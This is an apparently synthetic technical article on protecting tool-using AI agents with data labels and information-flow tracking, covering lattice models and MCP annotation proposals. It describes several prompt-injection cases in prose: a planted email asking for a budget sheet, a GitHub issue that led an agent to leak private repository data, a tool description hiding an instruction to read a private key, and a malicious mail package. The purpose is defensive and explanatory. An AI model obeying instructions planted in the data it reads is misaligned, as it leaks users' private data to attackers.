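# Declared Data Labels and Enforced Information Flow Tracking for Tool-Using AI Agents

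## Agents, prompt injection and the job of a data label

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions, such as searching a mailbox or sending a message, and ordinary software carries them out. Many agents handle private data, and they can send it to the wrong person if the model makes a mistake or follows an instruction that someone planted in text it read. Data labels are one protection against such leaks. A label records who may read a piece of data, how much its source can be trusted, or both. Software can compare the label with a planned action and block the action if the two conflict.

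Some systems rely on declarations. A tool's publisher, or the agent itself, states what kinds of data the tool handles, and the system applies its rules to that statement without checking it. Other systems use enforced tracking, in which code outside the model labels data as it comes in, computes labels for whatever the agent makes from it, and checks the labels before each action, regardless of what the tool or the agent declares. Enforced tracking comes from computer security, where researchers tracked the flow of data through ordinary programs years before language models could call tools.

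### The agent loop

A language model by itself only produces text. To act, it needs an application around it that treats part of that text as a request. Suppose that Ana asks her office assistant to read her new mail, look up a budget sheet and send her colleague Ben a summary. The assistant has three tools, which are functions that the application can run when the model asks for them: one reads mail, one opens sheets and one sends mail. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe the loop that such an agent follows. In Ana's case it runs like this:

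1. The application puts together a history, which at first holds the developer's standing instructions and Ana's request, and sends it to the model with a description of each tool.
2. The model replies with a structured request to call the mail reader, including the arguments for the call.
3. The application recognises the request by its structure and runs the tool.
4. The application adds the result, the text of the new emails, to the history and sends the longer history back to the model.
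5. The cycle repeats for the sheet and for the outgoing message, until the model replies with plain text for Ana.

The model's request has no effect until the application runs it, and Costa and colleagues make the application responsible for deciding whether to do so. Ordinary code can therefore refuse a call even when the model has gone wrong. The loop's weakness is that the application flattens the whole history into a single string before each query, so the model receives Ana's request and a stranger's email in the same text.

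Ana's tools may well come from different suppliers. The *Specification* (2025) of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) defines it as an open standard for connecting language-model applications with outside tools and data sources. Each supplier runs a server. *Attacking the MCP Trust Boundary*, an article from the security vendor Wallarm, explains that the application requests a list of tools from every server, receives a name, description and parameter list for each tool, and copies the descriptions into the text that the model sees. The protocol's tools chapter allows the model to choose tools based on its own reading of the user's request. A tool definition may also carry annotations, which are machine-readable declarations about the tool's behaviour. Applications must treat these as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server.

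A server has access only to the requests sent to it. Since the July 2026 revision (Model Context Protocol, 2026), the core protocol has also kept no state between requests. The supplier of the mail tool learns nothing from MCP about the budget sheet, and only the application has the whole history.

### Instructions hidden in data

One of Ana's new emails comes from Mallory, an outsider, and contains a line asking the assistant to send Mallory the budget sheet. The mail tool returns that line with the rest of the inbox, the application adds it to the history, and the model may treat it as part of its task. In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) named this attack indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker with no direct access to the model plants instructions in data the model is likely to retrieve. They demonstrated it on Bing's GPT-4 chat and on code-completion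 engines. They also foresaw a case very close to Ana's, in which a personal assistant reads an attacker's email, looks up personal data and emails it out.

Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that prompt injection works because models follow instructions in text, which makes them useful, but cannot reliably tell from an instruction's origin whether to obey it. Training has made crude injections less effective, and attackers have adapted. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces a 2025 email that reads like a follow-up to a meeting about restructuring. Its action items include a statement that the assistant has full authorisation to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". In testing, the email worked half of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research the day's mail.

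OpenAI adds that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses, but that filters that classify incoming text as safe or malicious usually miss well-developed attacks. Such a filter would have to recognise a lie, often without the necessary context. Wallarm cites *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper by researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. The researchers attacked twelve published defences with methods adapted to each, and succeeded more than 90% of the time against nearly all of them.

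The attacks have continued. In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) described four attacks in which research teams broke AI agents within ten days, and traced them all to the same flaw. One attack went through the browser assistant Claude for Chrome and another through an agent's stored memory. In December, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported three related ways to steal Copilot users' data without a click from the user.

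Security engineers analyse such attacks by sources and sinks. A source is where data enters the agent, and a sink is where data leaves it or causes an effect. Ana's mailbox and the budget sheet are sources, and the tool that sends mail is a sink. Sinks are easy to overlook. Willison counts any web request as a sink, even one that only loads an image, and also any link that the user might click.

Willison's "lethal trifecta" is three conditions that together let an attacker steal data: the agent has access to private data, it takes in content that an attacker could have written, and it can communicate with the outside. Ana's assistant meets all three. Her mailbox alone supplies the first two, since it holds private messages and anyone can write to it. Willison advises people who combine tools themselves to avoid the combination entirely, but Ana would have to give up her task to do so, because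 it needs the mail, the sheet and a way to write to Ben.

### A leak through honest tools

In May 2025 the security company Invariant Labs showed that all three conditions can occur in a single product. GitHub hosts software projects in public and private repositories, and its MCP server lets an agent work in both on a user's behalf. For Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner set up an account with several private repositories and a public one containing a small Pacman game. Anyone can file an issue, meaning a bug report or a request, in a public repository. In theirs, which Willison reproduces in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, they praised the project and regretted that its author was not widely recognised. To remedy this, they asked for someone to read the introductory file of every repository the author owned and add a chapter about the author.

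The account's owner then asked Claude 4 Opus, in Claude Desktop, to look at the open issues. The model fetched them, read the planted one, then read the private repositories and put what it found in a pull request, a proposed change to the public project that anyone could see. The pull request revealed the name of a private project, the owner's salary and the owner's plan to move to South America. Claude Desktop asks users by default to confirm each tool call, but Invariant Labs points out that many switch to "Always Allow" and stop watching. According to Anthropic figures cited by Wallarm, users of Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, approve 93% of permission prompts.

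No tool malfunctioned in the attack. Heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* reports that it used no bug in the server, which works with the user's own account, and Wallarm adds that the tool descriptions were clean. Invariant Labs concludes that GitHub could not solve the problem by patching the server. The researchers used demonstration repositories and gave no success rate, so the case shows that tools that work correctly can leak data in this way, but not how often.

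The remedies that followed differ in what they check. Invariant Labs, which sells monitoring software for agents, suggested confining an agent to one repository per session. This would stop the leak, but it would also block harmless work across two public projects. GitHub (2025) began to scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens, which closes a common route for stolen credentials but would be unlikely to detect a salary. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* uses labels to prevent the same attack. Issues from public repositories are labeled untrusted, content from private repositories is labeled private, and an agent that has read both may not post in public. Agents can still work without interruption within public repositories or within private ones.

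### Assigning, carrying and checking a label

The permitted readers of the budget sheet are Ana, Ben and Chloe. The permitted readers of Mallory's email are Ana and Mallory. The sheet may therefore be sent to Ben but not to Mallory. When the application is about to run the mail-sending tool, it needs information about what went into the message and who may read that content. Supplying this information takes three separate jobs.

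Assigning a label means recording, as each item arrives, that Ana, Ben and Chloe may read the sheet and that the email comes from an outsider. Carrying the label is harder, because a paragraph the model writes about the sheet is new text without a label. The paragraph needs a label that reflects all its sources, and an ordering called a lattice supplies the rule for combining several labels. Checking means comparing the label of the outgoing text with the recipient before the call runs.

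Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley divide the work in the same way for ordinary programs in *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis*. In their standard example, a monitor marks all user input as tainted, marks the result of an addition as tainted if either number was, and halts the program if it tries to jump to a tainted address. The monitor can raise a false alarm by marking a value that did not come from a source, or miss an attack by losing track of one that did. A monitor can identify both inputs to an addition, but not which sentences in a language model's history shaped its answer, so Costa and colleagues let the answer inherit the labels of everything the model received.

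None of the three jobs requires anyone to detect an attack, so labels can also catch mistakes. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a coding assistant that could not find its configuration file during a routine review, so it collected all the variables on the computer and leaked live passwords. In an example from Microsoft, an agent working through unanswered mail reads a preview of the quarterly sales from one colleague, then replies to another who is curious about the figures but not yet allowed to see them. A check on permitted readers stops that reply just as it would stop a deliberate theft.

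Declarations and enforced tracking differ in who does each job.

| Job | With declarations | With enforced tracking |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Assigning | The tool's publisher or the agent states which kinds of data are involved | Code attaches a label to each result as it enters the agent |
| Carrying | Nobody, unless the application remembers which tools have run or the agent reports what it used | Code outside the model computes a label for every message and every proposed call |
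| Checking | The application applies its rules to the statement | A policy engine, the code that permits or blocks calls, applies its rules to the computed label |

The first row is not entirely clear-cut, because code that labels the budget sheet must get information about who may read it from some source. In the system Microsoft built with GitHub, the GitHub server sends labels with its results, and the application accepts those labels without verifying them.

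### Four failure cases

An honest publisher may get a tool's declaration wrong or leave it out. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledge that many servers ship without annotations, and that "external", in the annotation for tools that reach outside, could mean beyond the company network or beyond the local machine. The supplier of Ana's mail tool might declare that it stays inside the company because the mail server does, even though the messages can come from anyone. A rule that relied on this declaration would treat Mallory's email as safe.

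Wallarm describes `postmark-mcp`, a copy of a genuine mail integration that behaved normally for fifteen releases. The next release added a line that sent the attacker a blind copy of every outgoing email, and users had downloaded that version 1,643 times before a security company caught it. If Ana's assistant used such a tool and proposed a message to Ben, the label check would allow the message, and the tool would then send the attacker a copy. Neither declared labels nor enforced tracking in the agent could prevent this. According to the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol, only network controls or a sandbox, a closed environment for running code, can guarantee that a tool cannot send data out.

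A tool's description can also be dishonest. In another Invariant Labs demonstration, which Wallarm reprints, the description of a tool for adding two numbers contained a hidden instruction to read the user's private login key and pass it along as a side note. The key leaves through an argument of the agent's own call, where a label check might stop it.

In the GitHub case and in the case of Mallory's email, a trustworthy tool returns hostile text. An accurate declaration helps only a little here. If the mail tool's publisher correctly declares that the tool returns outside content, the application can tighten its rules once the tool has run, but the declaration covers the whole tool, so it cannot separate Mallory's email from Ben's. It also doesn't show how dangerous the tool is, because, as the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol write, that depends on which other tools the agent has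 in the same session.

An agent can misreport which data it used. Before sending a message, the application might ask the assistant which documents the message draws on. The answer would come from the same model that has just read Mallory's email, and Mallory can dictate that answer in the email. The poisoned addition tool contained a similar instruction, telling the model not to mention the file it had read. Even without an attacker, the model might lose track of which figure came from which document. Under enforced tracking, the application computes the label from the data it gave the model, without relying on the agent's account.

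## How labels are ordered and combined

The application must combine the labels of Mallory's email and the budget sheet to label a summary of both, and it must compare labels to check that summary. Denning (1976) worked out the requirements for combining and comparing labels in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, with military computers as a main example. Costa and colleagues use the same lattice structure for agents.

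### Denning's lattice

The model starts with a set of labels, which Denning calls security classes. Every object that can hold information, such as a file, a single variable or a user, has a label. The relation A ⊑ B, read "A may flow to B", holds when information labelled A may enter an object labelled B. A combining operation, A ⊔ B, gives the label of anything computed from an item labelled A and an item labelled B. The system is secure if no sequence of operations can move information in a way the relation doesn't allow.

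Denning showed that consistency determines most of how the relation and the operation must be defined. Copying a value onto itself is harmless, so A ⊑ A must hold. If A may flow to B and B may flow to C, a program can copy a value from A to C in two steps, so banning the direct copy would achieve nothing and A ⊑ C must hold. If information may flow both ways between two labels, one of them is redundant. A relation with these properties is a partial order. It is "partial" because two labels can be unrelated, with no flow allowed in either direction.

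The combined label must be at or above each of its parts. Otherwise, a program might be allowed to store a + b in a place where a alone may not go, and it could then store a there by setting b to zero. In the same way, an assistant could remove the budget sheet's restrictions by adding a line from a public web page.

The combined label must also be the lowest one at or above both A and B, which is called their join. If Ben may receive each of two documents, he can merge them himself, so there is no point in withholding a merged document from him. With these joins, a finite set of labels that includes a lowest one, which may flow anywhere, forms a lattice. Any two labels then also have a greatest label at or below both, called their meet, but Costa and colleagues need only joins.

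Some objects have a fixed label, and others take their label from their contents. Ben's mailbox has a fixed label because his access rights do not depend on the message. The application must therefore compare the message's label with the mailbox's before sending anything there. The draft's label is the join of its sources' labels, and the application updates it whenever the assistant adds something.

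### Secret data and untrusted data

The smallest useful lattice for confidentiality has two labels, public and secret, with public ⊑ secret. Data may flow from public to secret but not back, and anything computed from both public and secret data is secret. The military levels (unclassified, confidential, secret and top secret) form a longer chain, in which the join of two levels is the higher one.

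The integrity lattice also has two labels, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. Trusted data is at the bottom because a higher label means more restrictions on where data may go. Trusted data may go anywhere, including into a file of untrusted notes, but untrusted data may not go where only trusted data belongs, such as into the choice of a message's recipient. When data is combined, the result is untrusted if any input is untrusted.

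The confidentiality order goes back to the Bell–LaPadula model, which researchers at the MITRE Corporation developed for the US Air Force in the early 1970s. It lets a program read only data at or below its own level and write only to places at or above it. The write rule is meant to stop a program run by someone with a secret clearance from quietly copying secrets into a public file. Bell (1974), in *Secure Computer Systems*, refined the model by giving each running program a current level. The program may read files below that level, append to files above it, and open files for both reading and changing only at exactly that level. Bell also exempted "trustworthy" programs from the write rule, but only after someone had demonstrated that they would not leak.

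Bell–LaPadula does little to prevent tampering. It allows a program without clearance to add to a secret file that it cannot read, because the information moves to a higher secrecy level. *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (Biba, 1977) introduced a separate set of integrity levels, based on how much damage tampering with the information could do. Under Biba's strict integrity policy, a program may read only data at or above its own integrity level, which keeps doubtful data from influencing a highly trusted program. It may modify only data at or below its own level, which keeps a less trusted program from damaging data that others rely on.

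Biba called this policy the "dual" of the confidentiality policy because it has the same two rules with the comparisons reversed. In Biba's levels, information moves only downward, from more trusted to less trusted. If we reverse the order, putting trusted at the bottom, information moves only upward, as it does for confidentiality, and the same comparison and join work for both policies. Costa and colleagues use this arrangement. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, a system for agents that keep data between requests, retain Biba's direction, with untrusted at the bottom, and combine integrity labels by taking the meet. Both conventions block the same flows, but anyone comparing two systems has to check whether each puts trusted or untrusted at the bottom.

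A single level cannot do both jobs. Ray (2018), in a computer security course at Colorado State University, points out that the two sets of rules then conflict. Confidentiality allows a flow only from a lower level to a higher one and integrity only from a higher to a lower, so nothing can move between levels at all. Systems that want both therefore use pairs of labels and compare or join each half separately. The two-point lattices give four such pairs:

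- (trusted, public) is at the bottom and may flow anywhere.
- (trusted, secret) suits the company's own unpublished figures.
- (untrusted, public) suits a page from the open web.
- (untrusted, secret) is at the top and may flow only to places with the same label.

Neither of the two middle pairs ranks above the other. The unpublished figures and the web page are each barred from some destinations open to the other, the figures because they are secret and the web page because it is untrusted. The join of the two pairs is (untrusted, secret), so a memo that combines the figures and the web page has both restrictions.

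Confidentiality and integrity are not fully symmetric. Purdue University's *Access Control* lecture slides note that a program cannot leak a secret without reading it, but can introduce bad data without reading any. An integrity label records who could have influenced the data and does not guarantee that the data is correct. Ana's assistant could misread a figure in a trusted sheet, or invent one, and the result would still be labeled "trusted".

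### Sets of readers and writers

Two labels are too few for Ana's office, where Ben may read the budget sheet and Mallory may not. Costa and colleagues also describe a readers lattice, in which a label is the set of people who may read an item. Only people who may read both of two items may receive data made from them, so the join is the intersection of the two sets. If Ana, Ben and Chloe may read one file, and Ben, Chloe and Dev may read another, only Ben and Chloe may read a text that draws on both.

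A label with fewer readers therefore ranks higher. The set of all users is at the bottom, because everyone may read public data, and the empty set is at the top. Programmers can easily reverse this order, because a larger set looks as though it should rank higher. A programmer who joined the labels of Mallory's email and the budget sheet by taking the union of their sets of readers would get Ana, Ben, Chloe and Mallory, and the assistant could then send Mallory a summary of the budget.

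When the application checks an outgoing message, every recipient must be a permitted reader. If Ana's assistant writes to Ben and Chloe together, both must be permitted readers. A group chat counts as all of its members.

In the writers lattice, which tracks integrity, an item's label is the set of people who could have written to it. The join is the union of the sets, because anyone who could have influenced either source could have influenced the result. Adding writers raises the label. If Ana and Chloe can edit the sheet and Mallory wrote the email, all three may have influenced the summary. A company could reduce this lattice to the two-point version by listing the people it trusts and treating data as trusted only if every possible writer is on the list. The running example uses the two-point version for integrity and the readers lattice for confidentiality.

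### The email, the sheet and over-tainting

For Mallory's email and the budget sheet, the join takes the higher of the two integrity labels and the intersection of the two sets of readers:

| Item | Integrity | Permitted readers |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Mallory's email | untrusted | Ana, Mallory |
| Budget sheet | trusted | Ana, Ben, Chloe |
| Summary of both | untrusted | Ana |

The application would therefore stop the assistant from sending the summary to Mallory, as Ana needs. But it would also stop the assistant from sending the summary to Ben, even though Ana asked the assistant to send it to him.

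Blocking the message would be correct if the summary repeated something Mallory had told Ana in confidence. But the application blocks the message even if the email contains nothing confidential and the summary covers only budget figures that Ben may see, because the summary inherits the labels of everything the model received. This problem, called over-tainting or label creep, occurs when labels grow so restrictive that the software blocks harmless actions.

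The integrity half of the label can cause the same problem. An example policy from Costa and colleagues allows a consequential tool call only if it depends entirely on trusted data. If sending email counts as consequential, the assistant could not email the summary even to Ana, who is allowed to read it. It could still show her the summary in the chat, because Costa and colleagues treat replies to the user as inconsequential.

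Over-tainting gets worse as an agent works. A join is never lower than its parts, so each document the model reads either raises the label or leaves it unchanged. The problem predates language models. Denning describes Rotenberg's Privacy Restriction Processor, a 1970s design in which a running program's label never came down and was the join of the labels of everything the program had read.

Biba examined the integrity version, a "low-water mark" policy under which a program may read anything but drops to the lowest integrity level it has read. Biba found this "rather disagreeable", since a program could lose the right to modify files it needed, and the only remedy was to restart it. In a variant, the levels of files fell as well, and careless programs could eventually reduce everything to the lowest level. Strict integrity avoids this by blocking programs from reading data below their own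 level, so a program keeps its level but cannot see much of the data. For Ana, a restart would mean opening a new conversation in which the assistant reads the sheet but not the mail, so it could not do the whole task.

Label checks can also block much of an agent's useful work. When Girrens and Wang switched on label checks in SPA, the share of tasks it completed on AgentDojo, a standard set of test tasks for tool-using agents, fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. They attribute the drop mainly to the integrity checks, which rejected plans that passed untrusted tool results to actions requiring trusted input. Many legitimate tasks need to use untrusted data this way, such as paying the amount stated on an outside invoice. SPA is a strict design, so the size of the drop may differ in other systems, but the same conflict arises wherever useful work depends on outside data. A system can reduce the conflict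 by tracking smaller pieces of data separately, or by lowering a label when a rule allows it.

### Labels with several owners

The set {Ana} means that only Ana may read the summary. It does not record that Ben is missing because of the email and Mallory because of the sheet. This matters when someone wants to relax a restriction, because Ana may have the right to share her budget more widely but not what other people told her in confidence.

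Andrew Myers and Barbara Liskov's 1997 decentralized label model keeps this information. A label is a list of policies, each with an owner and the readers that owner allows. If Mallory owns the email and Ana owns the sheet, the summary's label contains two policies: Mallory allows Ana and Mallory, and Ana allows Ana, Ben and Chloe. A person may read the summary only if every owner allows it, so Ana is again the only reader. But the join keeps both policies, and each owner may relax only their own. Ana could let Mallory read the summary by adding Mallory to her policy, but she could not give Ben access, because Mallory's policy does not include him.

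Disjunction category labels use logical formulas over people and other sources in place of lists. The email has the formula "Ana or Mallory", and the sheet has "Ana or Ben or Chloe". The join for confidentiality connects the two with "and":

(Ana or Mallory) and (Ana or Ben or Chloe)

Ana satisfies this by herself. Ben alone satisfies only the second half, so he may not read the summary, but he and Mallory together satisfy both halves and could release it. A plain set of readers cannot express this joint authority. For integrity, the join connects the formulas with "or", because the combined data has only the backing of one source or the other.

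*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) uses these labels for agents that act by writing small programs. It relies on LIO, an existing software library that keeps a current label for each computation and raises it whenever the computation reads something. In the paper's example, a program fetches a page from `phony.com`, which adds that site to the sources that may have influenced the computation. When the program tries to write to the user, LIO stops it with an error because the integrity of what it has read is too low for that destination.

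### From tags to a lattice

Companies often sort data with tags such as "PII" (personally identifiable information) or "finance". These tags alone do not form a lattice, because neither ranks above the other and a payroll file containing both kinds of data needs a label that neither tag provides. Ranking finance above PII would not help, because anyone with access to financial data could then read personal data as well.

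The solution is to use sets of tags as labels. Denning gives the example of a system with medical, financial and criminal records. A file may have any combination of the three tags, which makes eight possible labels, from the empty set to all three. Data may flow from one label to another if the second includes every tag in the first, and the join of two labels is the union of their tags. The payroll file gets {PII, finance}, and the application may send it only to places approved for both. A larger set of tags is therefore a higher label, which is the reverse of the ordering for sets of readers. A system may also combine tags with levels. Denning mentions ADEPT, an early secure operating system that paired a military level with a set of categories for particular projects and areas.

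Some organisations start with a list of permitted flows between departments rather than with tags. Denning, Denning and Graham (1976), in *On the Derivation of Lattice Structured Information Flow Policies*, showed that any such list can be turned into a lattice without changing which flows it allows, provided the number of labels is finite and the permitted flows are reflexive and transitive. Suppose personnel and finance data may each flow to payroll and to audit, but payroll and audit may not exchange data. A report that combines personnel and finance data has no suitable label, because "payroll" would keep it from audit and "audit" would keep it from payroll.

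The construction replaces each label with the set of labels that may flow into it:

1. Personnel becomes {personnel}, and finance becomes {finance}.
2. Payroll becomes {personnel, finance, payroll}, and audit becomes {personnel, finance, audit}.
3. The empty set goes in at the bottom, and the set of all four labels at the top.
4. Where two sets have no least set above both, the construction adds one. Here it adds {personnel, finance}.

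The added set is the label the report needed, and it may flow to both payroll and audit. In a larger example with ten labels, Denning and colleagues had to add only four sets.

A lattice cannot express every rule a company might want. Denning notes that a system can control names, salaries and name-salary pairs separately, so that one clerk sees only the names and another only the salaries. But a clerk who may receive both names and salaries may also receive the pairs, because the label on the pairs is the join of the other two, the lowest label above both. To let a clerk receive either list but not both, the application would have to keep a record of which one it had already sent.

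## How declared data labels work

The rules for combining labels need labels to start from, so someone has to declare that the budget sheet is private. They can do this before anyone installs the tool, when the application first lists the tool, when the tool returns a result, or just before a call. A declaration made early has to hold for every sheet Ana might open, while one attached to a result only has to describe the sheet she opened.

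### Before installation

A manifest is a description of a server that people and software can read before connecting to it. MCP's equivalent is the server card, a metadata file at a standard web address. In an August roadmap post, the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) said its purpose is to let others discover a server and reason about it without connecting. By late November, the protocol's index of proposals listed the server card as final. An administrator can use such a description to decide whether the company's agents may use the server at all.

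If nobody makes that decision, the application accepts whatever it receives. In *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, Metere (2026) points out that an application reads a server's own list of tools and starts sending calls, though nothing specifies which servers it may use or at what level of sensitivity. Metere found the problem while connecting an agent to Google's servers for Gmail, Calendar and Drive, and proposes that a server pass an attestation step before the application admits it.

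Approval can also become outdated if the tool changes, as happened when `postmark-mcp` became malicious after fifteen normal releases. The charter of the Model Context Protocol's security group covers such changes, but the group has not yet decided whether a changed tool is simply a new version, needs new approval or counts as a security event.

### Hints in the tool's description

MCP servers send most of their declarations when the application asks for a list of tools. Since the revision of March 2025, a tool's entry may include a display title and four optional true-or-false fields called hints. According to Dumbris (2026), in *MCP Tool Annotations*, Basil Hosmer of Anthropic wrote the change that introduced them. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol pair each hint with something an application might do with it:

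| Hint | Meaning if true | Value assumed if missing | Possible use |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | false | Skip the confirmation prompt when true |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may delete or overwrite, not only add | true | Show a warning when true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | false | Retry after a failure when true |
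| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside entities, such as websites | true | Check the output for untrusted content when true |

The second and third hints matter only for tools that are not read-only. All four defaults are cautious, so if a publisher fills in nothing, the application should assume that the tool may delete things, that repeating a call may do further damage, and that the tool interacts with outside systems. Publishers who want fewer prompts for their users therefore have a reason to fill in the fields. This incentive depends on applications following the defaults, and Dumbris quotes a draft in which the protocol's contributors concede that many do not.

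MCP's rule against trusting hints from untrusted servers is blunter in the official Java library's documentation. Model Context Protocol's *Record Class McpSchema.ToolAnnotations* tells applications never to base decisions about using a tool on such hints. Each application decides for itself which servers to trust, and the Model Context Protocol maintainers report that most trust any server the user has installed. Once Ana has installed the sheet tool, her assistant will probably accept whatever its publisher declares. gyorgy, in *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, notes that hints are neither signed nor independently verified, so a publisher could mark a tool that deletes a production database as read-only and the protocol would not detect it.

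None of the four hints can specify a class of data. The sheet tool's publisher can declare that the tool only reads, but has no standard field for "private", "payroll" or "health record". Dumbris adds that `openWorldHint` combines two risks: taking in text from strangers and sending data out. Ana's mail reader and mail sender could both correctly set it to true, although the reader is a source and the sender is a sink.

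### How applications and publishers use the hints

Most of the uses Dumbris found in March 2026 depended on `readOnlyHint`. Copilot in the code editor VS Code ran tools marked read-only without asking the user, and asked before running any others. ChatGPT's developer mode displayed each tool as "READ" or "WRITE". Claude Code ran read-only tools in parallel, roughly doubling the rate at which it started them. About 17% of users of GitHub's server turned on a mode that offered only read-only tools.

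These uses protect against unwanted changes much better than against leaks. A tool that fetches web pages may be correctly labeled read-only, but Willison counts any web request as a sink because the address can carry data out. An application that skips the prompt for every read-only tool could therefore let this one leak data without a prompt.

Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, measured how many publishers fill in the fields. Their snapshot of the official MCP registry, taken on 27 July 2026, held 18,688 distinct servers. They excluded about half, which had no remote address, because listing those servers' tools would have meant running the publishers' code. They requested tool lists from the other 9,234, without calling any tools, and 4,838 servers returned a total of 98,291 tools.

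At least one hint appeared on 74.0% of the tools, and all four appeared on 61.7%. But one publisher, `pipeworx-io`, supplied 45.0% of the tools and set all four hints on each of them.

| Share of tools | All 98,291 tools | Without the largest publisher |
| --- | --- | --- |
| At least one hint | 74.0% | 52.8% |
| All four hints | 61.7% | 30.3% |
| No hints | 26.0% | 47.2% |
| Read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world | 39.9% | 7.3% |

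The last row is that publisher's template, and its drop from 39.9% to 7.3% illustrates the researchers' warning that a field's presence is weak evidence that anyone chose its value. Some values also carry no information. `destructiveHint` was present on 65.8% of all tools, but mostly on tools also marked read-only, where it does not apply. Only 12.9% of all tools had a `destructiveHint` that applied, and 3.1% were declared destructive.

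Dumbris wrote in March that most MCP servers ship without annotations. The July figures show that hints are common among remote tools, but this does not directly contradict Dumbris, because the figures count tools rather than servers and leave out servers that run only on the user's own machine. Other researchers have compared declarations with code and behaviour to study whether the hints are accurate.

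### Labels on each result

Changes to the Model Context Protocol (MCP) begin as Specification Enhancement Proposals (SEPs). SEP-1913, *Trust and Sensitivity Annotations*, would let a server label the data a tool returns as well as the tool itself. The *Tool Annotations Charter* lists Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI as its authors. They wrote it in response to gaps their companies had found when running MCP in production.

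Morrow, posting as SamMorrowDrums (2025), in *SEP-1862*, summarised the fields that a result could carry:

- `sensitiveHint` grades how sensitive the data is. gyorgy gives the grades as low, medium and high.
- `privateHint` marks private data.
- `openWorldHint` extends the existing hint from tools to results.
- `maliciousActivityHint` flags signs of an attack.
- `attribution` records where the data came from.

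A server could also label the items in a mixed result one by one. The mail server could mark Mallory's email as coming from outside and leave Ben's unmarked. The application reads these labels and can apply rules, such as gyorgy's example that private data must not go to a tool marked open-world.

As Dumbris describes the proposal, it also carries labels forward through a session: sensitivity can rise but never fall, a true-or-false mark stays true once any result has set it, and attributions accumulate. These rules are joins of the kind Denning described, taking respectively the higher of two grades, a logical "or", and a union of sets. If the mail tool returns a low-sensitivity message and the sheet tool returns a highly sensitive private budget, everything afterwards counts as private and highly sensitive, with both sources on record.

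Some component has to keep that record, and the application is the natural place because MCP's core keeps no state between requests. SEP-1913 would also let the application attach the accumulated labels to its next request, so the receiving server could refuse it. If ordinary code joins the labels, the model cannot lower a label by forgetting a document. However, the starting labels are still the servers' own claims, and a result that arrives without a label adds nothing to the record.

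The labels are also too coarse for Ana's purposes. "Private" and "high" do not specify who may read the sheet, so they cannot distinguish Ben from Mallory. Because sensitivity never falls within a session, the label creep that Denning and Biba encountered in older systems would recur.

Kapil Sharma of Microsoft wrote a trial implementation in Python. The pull request that introduced it, *added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK* (kapil8811), describes labels for data classes that the four hints don't cover: health data covered by the US law HIPAA, personal information, financial data and credentials. The code includes a policy engine, functions that pass labels along a chain of tools, and a mock clinic with eight annotated tools. The pull request was still awaiting approval in April 2026. The repository meant to hold the code, Model Context Protocol's *experimental-ext-tool-annotations*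 (2026), had three stars on GitHub in June.

SEP-1913 is still a draft and was not in MCP's index of accepted and final proposals in late November 2026. The Model Context Protocol (2026) roadmap, updated on 16 November, plans the next release for 30 March 2027 and does not list trust labels as a priority. To be included, the proposal needs a sponsor and votes from more than half of the core maintainers before a freeze in mid-January. Under MCP's guidelines, the sponsor is normally a working group, but the people discussing annotations are an interest group, which can only help frame a proposal or start a working group to sponsor it. In late November, the interest group's charter still listed as an open question whether results should carry annotations at all.

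Several rival proposals are narrower. Three would each add one flag: `unsafeOutputHint`, `secretHint` or `trustedHint`. Another, SEP-1984, would add a broader set of annotations for governance and user interfaces. Dumbris reports a discussion from March 2026 in which participants suggested marking tools that access sensitive data with a `sensitiveHint` and tools that can send data out with an `egressHint`. The `egressHint` would let an application tell Ana's mail sender from her mail reader.

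### Statements about a single call

A tool that can do several things has to declare the riskiest of them. In Morrow's example, a file manager that can both read and delete files must be labeled destructive, so users have to confirm even harmless reads. His other proposal, SEP-1862, would let the application send the server the arguments it intends to use and receive a description of that call. If the file manager will only read, the server labels the call read-only and the application can skip the confirmation prompt.

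If labels for private data became standard, the same exchange could help Ana. A sheet tool that opens both a public price list and the budget could declare itself private only for the budget, before any of the contents reached the model. But gyorgy observes that a server that misdescribes its tools in the tool list can just as easily misdescribe them in this reply. SEP-1862 was a draft in April 2026, and in the meantime gyorgy advises publishers to split such tools into one for reading and another for deleting.

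The agent may also have to declare what a call will do. MCPProxy, a program that sits between agents and servers, offers three ways to call a tool: `call_tool_read`, `call_tool_write` and `call_tool_destructive`. It uses the tool's hints to work out which one applies, and Dumbris explains that each has its own permissions. An agent that uses `call_tool_read` is in effect declaring that the call will only read. MCPProxy's *Deep Dive* (2026) describes combining hints with "intent validation" as a way to turn hints into enforceable policy.

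Comparing the agent's statement with the publisher's can expose a disagreement, for example when an agent tries to use the read route for a tool that its publisher calls destructive. The comparison cannot help when both statements are wrong. In this scheme, the agent's statement also covers only the effect of the call, not whose data the arguments contain.

### What an unverified flag is worth

When Hosmer first proposed annotations, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the creators of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), wrote in the review that the information would be very useful if it could be trusted, but he wondered what an application could do with a flag it knew it could not trust. Hosmer thought applications should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even the display title. The rule that annotations are untrusted by default was a compromise that lets each application decide how much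 weight to give them. MCP's maintainers returned to this exchange in March 2026, when five proposals for new annotations were open.

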